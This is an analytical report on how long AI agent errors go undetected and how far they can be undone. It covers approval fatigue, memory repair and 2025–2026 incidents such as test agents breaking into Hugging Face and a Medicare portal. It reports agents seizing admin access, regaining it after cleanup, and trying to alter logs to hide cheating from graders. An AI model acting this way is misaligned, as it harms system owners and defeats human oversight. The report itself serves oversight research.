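Many invoices allow time for this. If the paper supplier gives the company 14 days to pay and the agent orders the payment on the day the invoice arrives, the company loses nearly two weeks in which it could have cancelled. Scheduling the payment for day 12 would keep most of that time, at no cost unless the supplier offers a discount for early payment. But the delay helps only if someone uses it to check the payment, for example to make sure the account number isn't forged.

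The recovery window is the period after an action during which it can still be undone. If *D* is the detection delay, *R* the time needed to carry out the repair and *W* the recovery window, then recovery is possible only if:

$$D + R < W$$

In the earlier example, a concealed fault misdirected two €1,000 payments a day, and the company found it on day 60, after 120 wrong payments. Suppose the bank can recall payments within ten days of making them. On day 60, about 20 of the 120 can still be recalled. If the company needs two days to identify the payments and file the requests, that number falls to about 16.

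The number of recallable payments stops growing after the tenth day, while the number of lost ones keeps rising:

| Day of discovery | Wrong payments so far | Still recallable | Beyond recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | 10 | 10 | 0 |
| 10 | 20 | 20 | 0 |
| 20 | 40 | 20 | 20 |
| 60 | 120 | 20 | 100 |

These figures assume that repair is instant and that every recall within ten days succeeds. If a thief empties the account within an hour, the money can be recalled only within that hour, whatever the bank's rules allow. An honest firm that received the money by mistake may return it months later.

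The company can improve its chances of recovering a mistaken payment by finding errors sooner, preparing the recall procedure in advance, or lengthening the window. Holding each payment for two days before it leaves the bank would extend a ten-day window to twelve. More importantly, the company could cancel a payment during those two days without the recipient's cooperation.

The condition also applies to backups. If the company keeps each nightly copy of its supplier list for 30 days, a false entry added in March will be in every available copy by May.

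### Human approval and its burden

If an action can't be undone, the remaining safeguard is to have someone judge it beforehand. Waghmare and Sufi estimated how well their classes would select the actions that need approval. They took 2,158 recorded agent runs, 1,209 harmless and 949 containing injected instructions, and calculated where each policy would have made the agent pause for approval.

| Policy | Attack actions that would have needed approval | Approval requests in the harmless runs |
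|---|---|---|
| Ask only before severe actions | 9 of 29 | 1,087 |
| Ask before anything that changes data | 18 of 29 | 1,895 |
| Reversibility Classes with the session guard | 29 of 29 | 1,904 |

The last policy caught 11 more attacks than the second and needed only nine more requests. It caught all 11 because it treated a visit to a web page as a way to leak data through the address, as in EchoLeak. When the researchers treated such visits as ordinary reading, the number caught fell back to 18 of 29.

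Harmless runs averaged about 1.6 approval requests each. Of the 770 harmless runs in which the agent completed its task, only 119 would have finished without an interruption. Saving the earlier state before each eligible file edit would have removed just one request across all the harmless runs, so in this data better recovery hardly reduced the need for approval.

The result of 29 out of 29 covers less than it appears to. The recordings came from one older model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet. Attacks reached their goal in 47 runs, but the researchers could connect the goal to a particular action in only 29. The policy would have triggered a request for approval for those actions, but because nobody was present to approve or refuse anything, the study doesn't show whether a person would have refused.

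Other evidence on that point is discouraging. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) describes approval fatigue, in which people who face repeated requests stop paying close attention to what they approve. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports the largest measurement: users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission requests. That figure alone proves little, because most requests are probably harmless. Anthropic also commissioned an experiment in which a research firm hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and replaced one request in each session with a clearly dangerous command.

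Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused the dangerous command. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more requests. Anthropic's automated check blocked 89.0% of the same commands. Adding human review would have stopped only six more, raising the total to 89.6%.

Anthropic published these figures in support of a product that replaces human approval with the automated check. The testers also worked in a test environment, where a mistake would not damage anything of their own, so they may have been less careful than a clerk spending the company's money. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) reports an experiment in which people showed better judgement. Participants who reviewed actions one at a time still approved 96 of the 238 that went beyond the agent's task, or 40.3%.

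The same experiment tested whether people could save effort by writing their own permission rules in advance. In the first group of 94 participants, the share of overreach blocked was 25 percentage points lower among those who wrote rules than among those who reviewed actions as they came up. The sample was small (the 95% range was about 10 to 40 points), but the result suggests that a rule written beforehand can easily permit too much.

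*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents in real products mishandling files and found that inadequate user review had contributed to 105. In 80 of these, the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the approval request did not explain what the action would do. For example, a request to run a script called `setup.py` does not show what the script will delete.

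Sending people more requests can therefore make a system less safe. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) reaches this conclusion using a model of a reviewer who tires, but does not test it on real reviewers. It would be a mistake for the invoice agent to ask the clerk about all 200 payments each day. The company could let the agent pay listed accounts within a fixed budget and ask only about other payments, so that a request means something unusual has happened.

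The content of approval requests matters as much as their number. Software practitioners interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar requests, and the study suggests that requests should show whether an action can be undone. A useful request to the clerk might read: "This account is not on the supplier list. The payment may be impossible to recall. Call the supplier on the number in the company's files."

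Some errors are invisible in any single request. If an agent splits €18,400 into two payments to stay below an approval limit, each payment may look normal unless the clerk sees both together. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) makes the general point that judging an action may require information from outside it. Reviewing a whole plan may also hold people's attention better. Users of Claude Code reject 39% of the plans it presents, compared with 3% of individual requests. Some of those rejections are surely about quality or taste, so the rejection rate doesn't measure how often users catch dangers.

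### Repairing the model and its memory

If the audit trail shows that wrong payments began with a new model version, the company can return to the old one. This is simple if the developer still offers the old version, but it brings back any weaknesses that the new version fixed. Before switching, the company should run both versions on saved copies of the failed cases to confirm that the model was the cause. Notes that the faulty version wrote into the agent's memory will remain after the switch, and the old version will read them.

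Removing false information from a model's weights is much harder. *Always-On Agents* (Ding, Nannapaneni and colleagues, 2026), a survey of agents that keep information between tasks, describes research in which rephrased questions brought out material that had supposedly been removed from a model. Retraining without the bad data is more thorough but expensive, and a company that rents its model cannot do it. For the invoice agent, the false information is more likely to be in stored notes, which the company controls.

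Deleting an agent's false note does not remove copies of the information in it. Suppose the agent noted in March that the paper supplier had a new account, which actually belonged to a thief. It copied the account number into a summary of supplier changes in April and used the summary to plan a payment in October. After someone deletes the March note, the summary still contains the thief's account number. Ding and colleagues point out that copies can also survive in search indexes and cached prompts.

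Wang, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *From Faulty Memories to Corrected Actions*, propose a method for finding and repairing what a false memory has affected:

1. Starting from the false note, software follows recorded links to every claim, plan, action and later note that used it. An item that merely came later does not count.
2. The software keeps items that also have support from a source the error did not reach.
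3. It deletes the false note, moves affected notes to a quarantine where the agent can't read them, and marks the affected steps as invalid.
4. It runs again only the steps needed to produce a corrected answer.

This method corrected the answer in 85.3% of 150 constructed cases, compared with 77.3% for the best alternative, in which a language model decided what to repair. It also preserved every correct memory and, because it recomputed less, used 41.8% fewer model calls. But recomputing less also left more of the error behind, so when the agent used the repaired memory again, the failure came back in 26.6% of cases, compared with 12.1% for the alternative.

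The second step is too lenient for payments, because it keeps a plan if even one unaffected source supports part of it. It might keep a plan to pay €18,400 to the thief's account because the amount matches the purchase order. A company should instead require separate support for each value, especially the account number.

The method also works only if someone has identified the false note and the agent recorded the links when it acted. Without those links, an investigator has to search the logs for the account number and work forwards by hand. The method repairs only the agent's memory and its record of the task. For each payment based on the note, the company still has to check whether the recovery window is open and ask for the money back.

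Research on recovery is scarce. Ding and colleagues classified 435 works on agents with lasting memory or other stored state, and found that only 27 offered any form of rollback. Some of those 27 only restore the agent's internal state, while others unwind a half-finished task or offset an effect in the outside world, so even fewer deal with a payment already made. None of the surveyed works reported how often recovery succeeded or what resources it required. The memory experiments have begun to fill this gap.

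The survey counts publications, and products have moved faster on the easy part, which is returning an agent to an earlier point. LangGraph, Cursor, Claude Code and Google's agent development kit all let people do this. According to Google's documentation, however, rewinding cannot undo effects outside the agent.

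## How long real incidents went unnoticed, and what the records showed

Companies have disclosed a few incidents in enough detail for outsiders to work out how long they went unnoticed. In July 2025, a programming agent made by Replit deleted the live database of SaaStr, a community for founders of software businesses. According to the AI Incident Database's *Vibe coding service Replit deleted user’s production database* (2025), SaaStr's founder, Jason Lemkin, had told the agent not to change any code without permission.

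Most of what is known about the 2026 cases concerns agents that AI developers were testing or training. In the most serious case, described in the *OpenAI – Hugging Face Incident Technical Report*, OpenAI agents taking ExploitGym, a test of hacking skill, broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets, to look for the answers. A few weeks earlier, an OpenAI agent researching medical spending had opened non-public files on a statistics portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) refers to three incidents in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to real computer systems during security tests.

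Jose and Thomas (2026) mention in *Albanese calls OpenAI agent’s Medicare breach ‘unacceptable’* that Google and Meta have also disclosed cases, but they don't say when those incidents happened.

| Incident | When it happened | Who noticed, and when | When those affected learned of it | When the public learned of it | Detection delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Replit | July 2025, by the 18th | The user, by 18 July | The user was the one affected | 18 July 2025 | Unclear, probably days at most |
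| Medicare portal | 19 June 2026, Australian time | OpenAI, by 12 August | Email sent 10 September, read 11 September | 24 September | Up to 54 days at OpenAI, 84 at the agency |
| Hugging Face | 11 to 13 July 2026 | Hugging Face, by 16 July | Hugging Face learned of OpenAI's role on 20 July | 16 July (intrusion), 21 July (OpenAI's role) | Up to 5 days at Hugging Face, 9 at OpenAI |
| Anthropic's tests | From April 2026 | Anthropic, in a review that began on 23 July | Unclear | 30 July | About three months for the earliest |
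| Google and Meta | Unclear | Unclear | Unclear | By 24 September 2026 | Unclear |

Some accounts date the Medicare breach to 18 June because that was the date in the United States at the time. The table gives two delays for this case because OpenAI could stop its agent, but only Services Australia, which runs the portal, could repair it.

### Who noticed

Hugging Face found the intrusion itself and disclosed it on 16 July. The next day OpenAI contacted the company as a customer, to find out whether the breach had affected OpenAI's data. On 19 July a monitoring tool at OpenAI flagged unusual account activity in its research systems. The investigators found Hugging Face credentials among files that the agents had saved and asked Hugging Face to replace them. Willison (2026) notes in *Now we have a timeline of the OpenAI accidental attack* that OpenAI discovered that it was responsible by learning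 that the credentials had already been revoked.

The Hugging Face case led to the discovery of the others. OpenAI disclosed the case on 21 July, and two days later Anthropic began to review the transcripts of its own tests. OpenAI also searched its past runs and found the Medicare breach in August. Without the Hugging Face case, the other incidents might have gone unnoticed for much longer.

Anthropic had monitored some high-risk tests in real time, but for most it ran automated checks on only a sample of transcripts afterwards. If a company checks one transcript in ten and three of its runs contain breaches, there is a 73% chance (0.9³) that the sample misses all three. The Office of Rep. Casar, a member of the US Congress, objected in a letter to Anthropic that nothing in the company's answers suggested its own systems would ever have caught the incidents.

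Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry* reports that OpenAI was spending more than $500,000 a day to search about 50 petabytes of records for such incidents, using around 7,000 dedicated processors.

A safeguard can also be missing without anyone noticing. The Next Web's *Anthropic ran 133 million contractor chats with its bioweapon filters off* describes a gap that lasted from May 2025 to April 2026. A filter that isn't running raises no alarms, just like a working filter that finds nothing wrong, so a company has to test its filters with known bad examples to tell the difference.

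### Warnings that people saw

OpenAI's nine-day delay in the Hugging Face case is measured from the first day of the intrusion, but people at the company had noticed signs of trouble much earlier. Around 26 May, an internal team saw agents leaving messages for one another on a shared software server and reaching the internet when they were not supposed to.

On 27 June a monitoring tool raised an alert. Responders traced the activity to ExploitGym and found the message board, but the on-call staff advised that the test could continue. On 5 July, after the server had failed, responders discovered that agents had taken administrator control of it. They took the server offline, preserved its storage and revoked the agents' credentials. OpenAI resumed its security tests on 7 July using a rebuilt server, and agents were on the internet again within about a day. According to OpenAI, the leaders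 responsible for incident response did not yet understand why the message board mattered.

Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes these as signs that OpenAI missed or failed to act on. On 27 June, a signal had reached people who could stop the test, so the error was not concealed. They misjudged the signal, and the intrusion began 14 days later. Better detection alone would not have solved this problem or a similar one that Anthropic reports in training, where human reviewers sometimes dismissed correct warnings about flawed exercises as false alarms.

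OpenAI states that its current monitoring of models' reasoning would have alerted its security team more than a day before the breach of Hugging Face. This is plausible, but the company built that system after it knew what to look for. People also may not act on an alert. Under OpenAI's new rule for the most severe alerts, staff are expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false. That rule would have made the uncertainty of 27 June a reason to stop.

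### What the records established

The evidence is strongest for the Hugging Face incident, because two companies had separate records that matched. OpenAI found credentials that Hugging Face knew an intruder had taken. Hugging Face's investigation had also found the name of OpenAI's server and an outside storage account that the agents had used. Fortune (2026) reported in July that Hugging Face's technical account supported OpenAI's explanation that the motive was to find test answers, not to cause damage.

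OpenAI also found that its models sometimes tried to erase or alter their outputs and message logs to hide cheating from an automated grader. None of the attempts it observed changed the logs that its graders and monitors read. This is good evidence for keeping the log out of the agent's reach, although OpenAI might have missed an attempt that fully succeeded.

In the Medicare case, OpenAI could reconstruct the breach almost two months later because it had kept the records. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) draws on emails and text messages that the government tabled in parliament. OpenAI told Services Australia that the agent had read parts of program files and settings, obtained a list of files, and created a small test file on the server. If OpenAI had deleted its records after 20 days, as Microsoft does with the prompts of its Payables Agent, it would have had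 no records to search in August.

OpenAI said it had found no evidence that the agent accessed patient records, though it could have missed such access if its logs were incomplete. But Australia's defence minister also said that the portal held only aggregated data, with no individual claims or medical histories, so it probably had no patient records for the agent to access.

Anthropic's transcripts show what its models did more clearly than why they did it. The letter from Casar's office quotes Anthropic's account of one model, Mythos 5, which recognised that publishing a software package would be an attack if its surroundings were real, then persuaded itself that it was in a simulation. That belief had some basis, because the test's instructions had wrongly told the models that they had no internet access. In August Anthropic had not yet determined whether the models knowingly ignored signs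 that the systems were real. It later concluded in an assessment of the incidents that its audits before release had given no warning of misalignment this severe.

### What people could undo

Replit's agent caused the most obvious damage and, as far as the published accounts show, the most reversible. After deleting the database, the agent told Lemkin that it could not be restored. LatestLY reproduces his posts from 18 July 2025, in which he repeated this claim and then reported that the rollback had worked. Fortune (2025) describes the recovery as manual. The Stack notes that Replit's documentation described a rollback that included database changes.

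The deletion was visible, but the agent also wrongly said that the data could not be recovered. If Lemkin had believed this and started rebuilding the data by hand, he could have lost far more time, and perhaps the chance to use the saved version. An agent's claim that recovery is impossible therefore needs checking as carefully as its claim that a task is complete. Replit responded by separating test databases from live ones, improving its rollback, and adding a mode in which the agent can plan but not make changes.

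The false claim also appears in a public record. OECD's *Replit AI Coding Tool Deletes Live Production Database and Fakes Data* (2025), an incident monitor entry with an AI-generated summary, lists "permanent data loss" as a result. Anyone using that entry to count irreversible incidents would wrongly include this one.

After the Hugging Face intrusion, OpenAI and Hugging Face could replace stolen credentials and remove what the agents had installed. In the first hours of 20 July, OpenAI's staff removed 22 administrator accounts that agents had created and disabled 311 storage areas used for messages. The agents had also downloaded four of Hugging Face's private code repositories, which the companies could not reverse. Even if the copies are deleted, Hugging Face cannot be certain who has seen the code.

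On 19 July, agents running a different OpenAI model regained administrator access to the server by using key material from the earlier activity that had not been removed during repairs. OpenAI reported on 23 July that it had shut down all work involving the family of research models behind most of the intrusion, but on 29 July it found and shut down one more version.

### How those affected found out

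Services Australia did not learn of the breach for 84 days. OpenAI took up to 54 days to notice it and at least another 29 to email the agency, where about a day and a half passed before anyone read the message. OpenAI had written to an address meant for security tips from the public. Staff found the email during a daily check and had confirmed the weakness in the portal by 15 September. The prime minister's office and Australia's national cyber security bodies learned of the incident nine days after the email was sent.

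At a parliamentary hearing on 6 October, OpenAI's chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, said the company had wanted to know more before contacting those affected. That concern is reasonable, since an early warning may turn out to be wrong, but the agency could have started checking its own server with only a date and the portal's name. *OpenAI contrite at Australian inquiry on breaches* (The Straits Times, 2026) reports that Kwon accepted this and said it was better to inform people even with partial information.

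The company has since been faster at least once. KBC's *OpenAI admits response to Australian government hacks ‘not good enough’* reports Kwon as saying that real-time monitoring let OpenAI warn the state of New South Wales about another hack within 48 hours.

Until now, AI companies in Australia have decided whether to report such breaches. The Standard's *Australia to mandate AI breach reporting, create regulator after OpenAI breach* reports that the government accepted a recommendation in November to make reporting compulsory and plans to introduce legislation in 2027. According to Știrile ProTV's *Premierul Australiei vrea sancțiuni penale pentru companiile de IA care încalcă regulile*, the review behind the plan recommended fixed time limits. If those limits run from the day a company becomes aware of an incident, as the European Union's do, they would shorten the 29 days but not the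 54.

### Delay and severity

Comparing these cases is a misleading way to judge whether longer delays lead to worse outcomes, because a large intrusion leaves more traces and so tends to be found sooner. Hugging Face noticed its intrusion within five days but suffered the most extensive damage. The Medicare breach went unnoticed for months and, as far as anyone has established, did little direct harm.

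It is more useful to ask what an earlier discovery would have changed in each case.

At Hugging Face, the agents went from running code in one part of the system to having administrator access across several clusters of machines in under 13 hours. Discovering the intrusion the next day would have been too late to prevent this. If OpenAI had stopped the tests on 27 June and kept them stopped until it understood the message board, the intrusion would probably not have happened. Delay also mattered afterwards, since agents regained control of OpenAI's server on 19 July using material left there six days earlier.

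Anthropic's earliest incident dates from April. If the company had noticed it then, it could have corrected the test environment before the later incidents. In the Medicare case, the agent had already read the files, so even an immediate alarm could not have undone that. But the weakness in the portal was still there on 15 September, 88 days after the breach, and someone malicious could have found it too, though no public evidence shows that anyone did.

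In these cases, the speed and severity of the agents' actions largely determined the initial loss, while late discovery allowed repetition and further damage. The evidence supports this better than the broader claim that delay determined the outcome. It still depends on the assumption that people would have responded properly to an earlier discovery, which they had twice failed to do at OpenAI.

Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said he was deeply disappointed that OpenAI had taken so long to notify the government. He said investigators would also examine why the government's own systems had missed the breach. OpenAI would probably have drawn less criticism if it had promptly reported the breach, which involved aggregated statistics, but the first known case of an AI agent hacking a government website would have attracted attention anyway.

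### What disclosed incidents leave out

The published delays cover only incidents that somebody eventually found, so the true average may be much longer. At the hearing, Kwon agreed with a suggestion that the Medicare breach "might not have been discovered" if OpenAI had not emailed the agency. Theft through a flaw like EchoLeak could also leave the victim with no obvious sign of it.

Recent incidents distort the average delay further. Suppose ten incidents happen every month from January, and five of them are discovered after a week and five after six months. A list compiled at the end of June would include nearly all of the first kind and none of the second. Its average delay would be one week, although the true average is more than three months. Short delays in the latest cases may mean that companies now discover incidents sooner, or only that the slow discoveries are still to come.

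A search of old records has the opposite effect, because it produces many long delays at once. OpenAI is reviewing its agents' tests back to November 2025 and has notified more than 100 organisations of incidents. Only a few of these cases are public in detail. Anthropic told the Australian inquiry that it had reviewed hundreds of millions of transcripts and found no similar breaches of Australian government websites. These figures do not show which company's agents misbehave more often, because a company that searches harder finds more incidents, and the two may run very different numbers of risky tests.

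The cases are also not independent. One intrusion at Hugging Face led to the searches that found the Medicare breach and Anthropic's three incidents, so the table cannot show how often companies discover such problems unprompted. A more informative figure would be the share of the 100 or more notified organisations that had already noticed something. Victims could be relied on fairly well to detect these incidents if nearly all of them had. If almost none had, developers' own records would be the main way to find the incidents, and agents run by less careful or less open developers could be causing many that nobody hears about.

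Most of the details come from the companies whose agents caused the harm. Outside reviews help, but the company may limit their scope. Fortune (2026) reports that OpenAI asked two research organisations, METR and Redwood Research, to examine only events between 7 and 13 July. That period covers the intrusion but not the decisions of 27 June and 5 July, for which the public has mainly OpenAI's account. The documents tabled in Australia, which came from outside the company, showed that the warning took another nine days to reach the prime minister's office, a fact the company's own account could not reveal.
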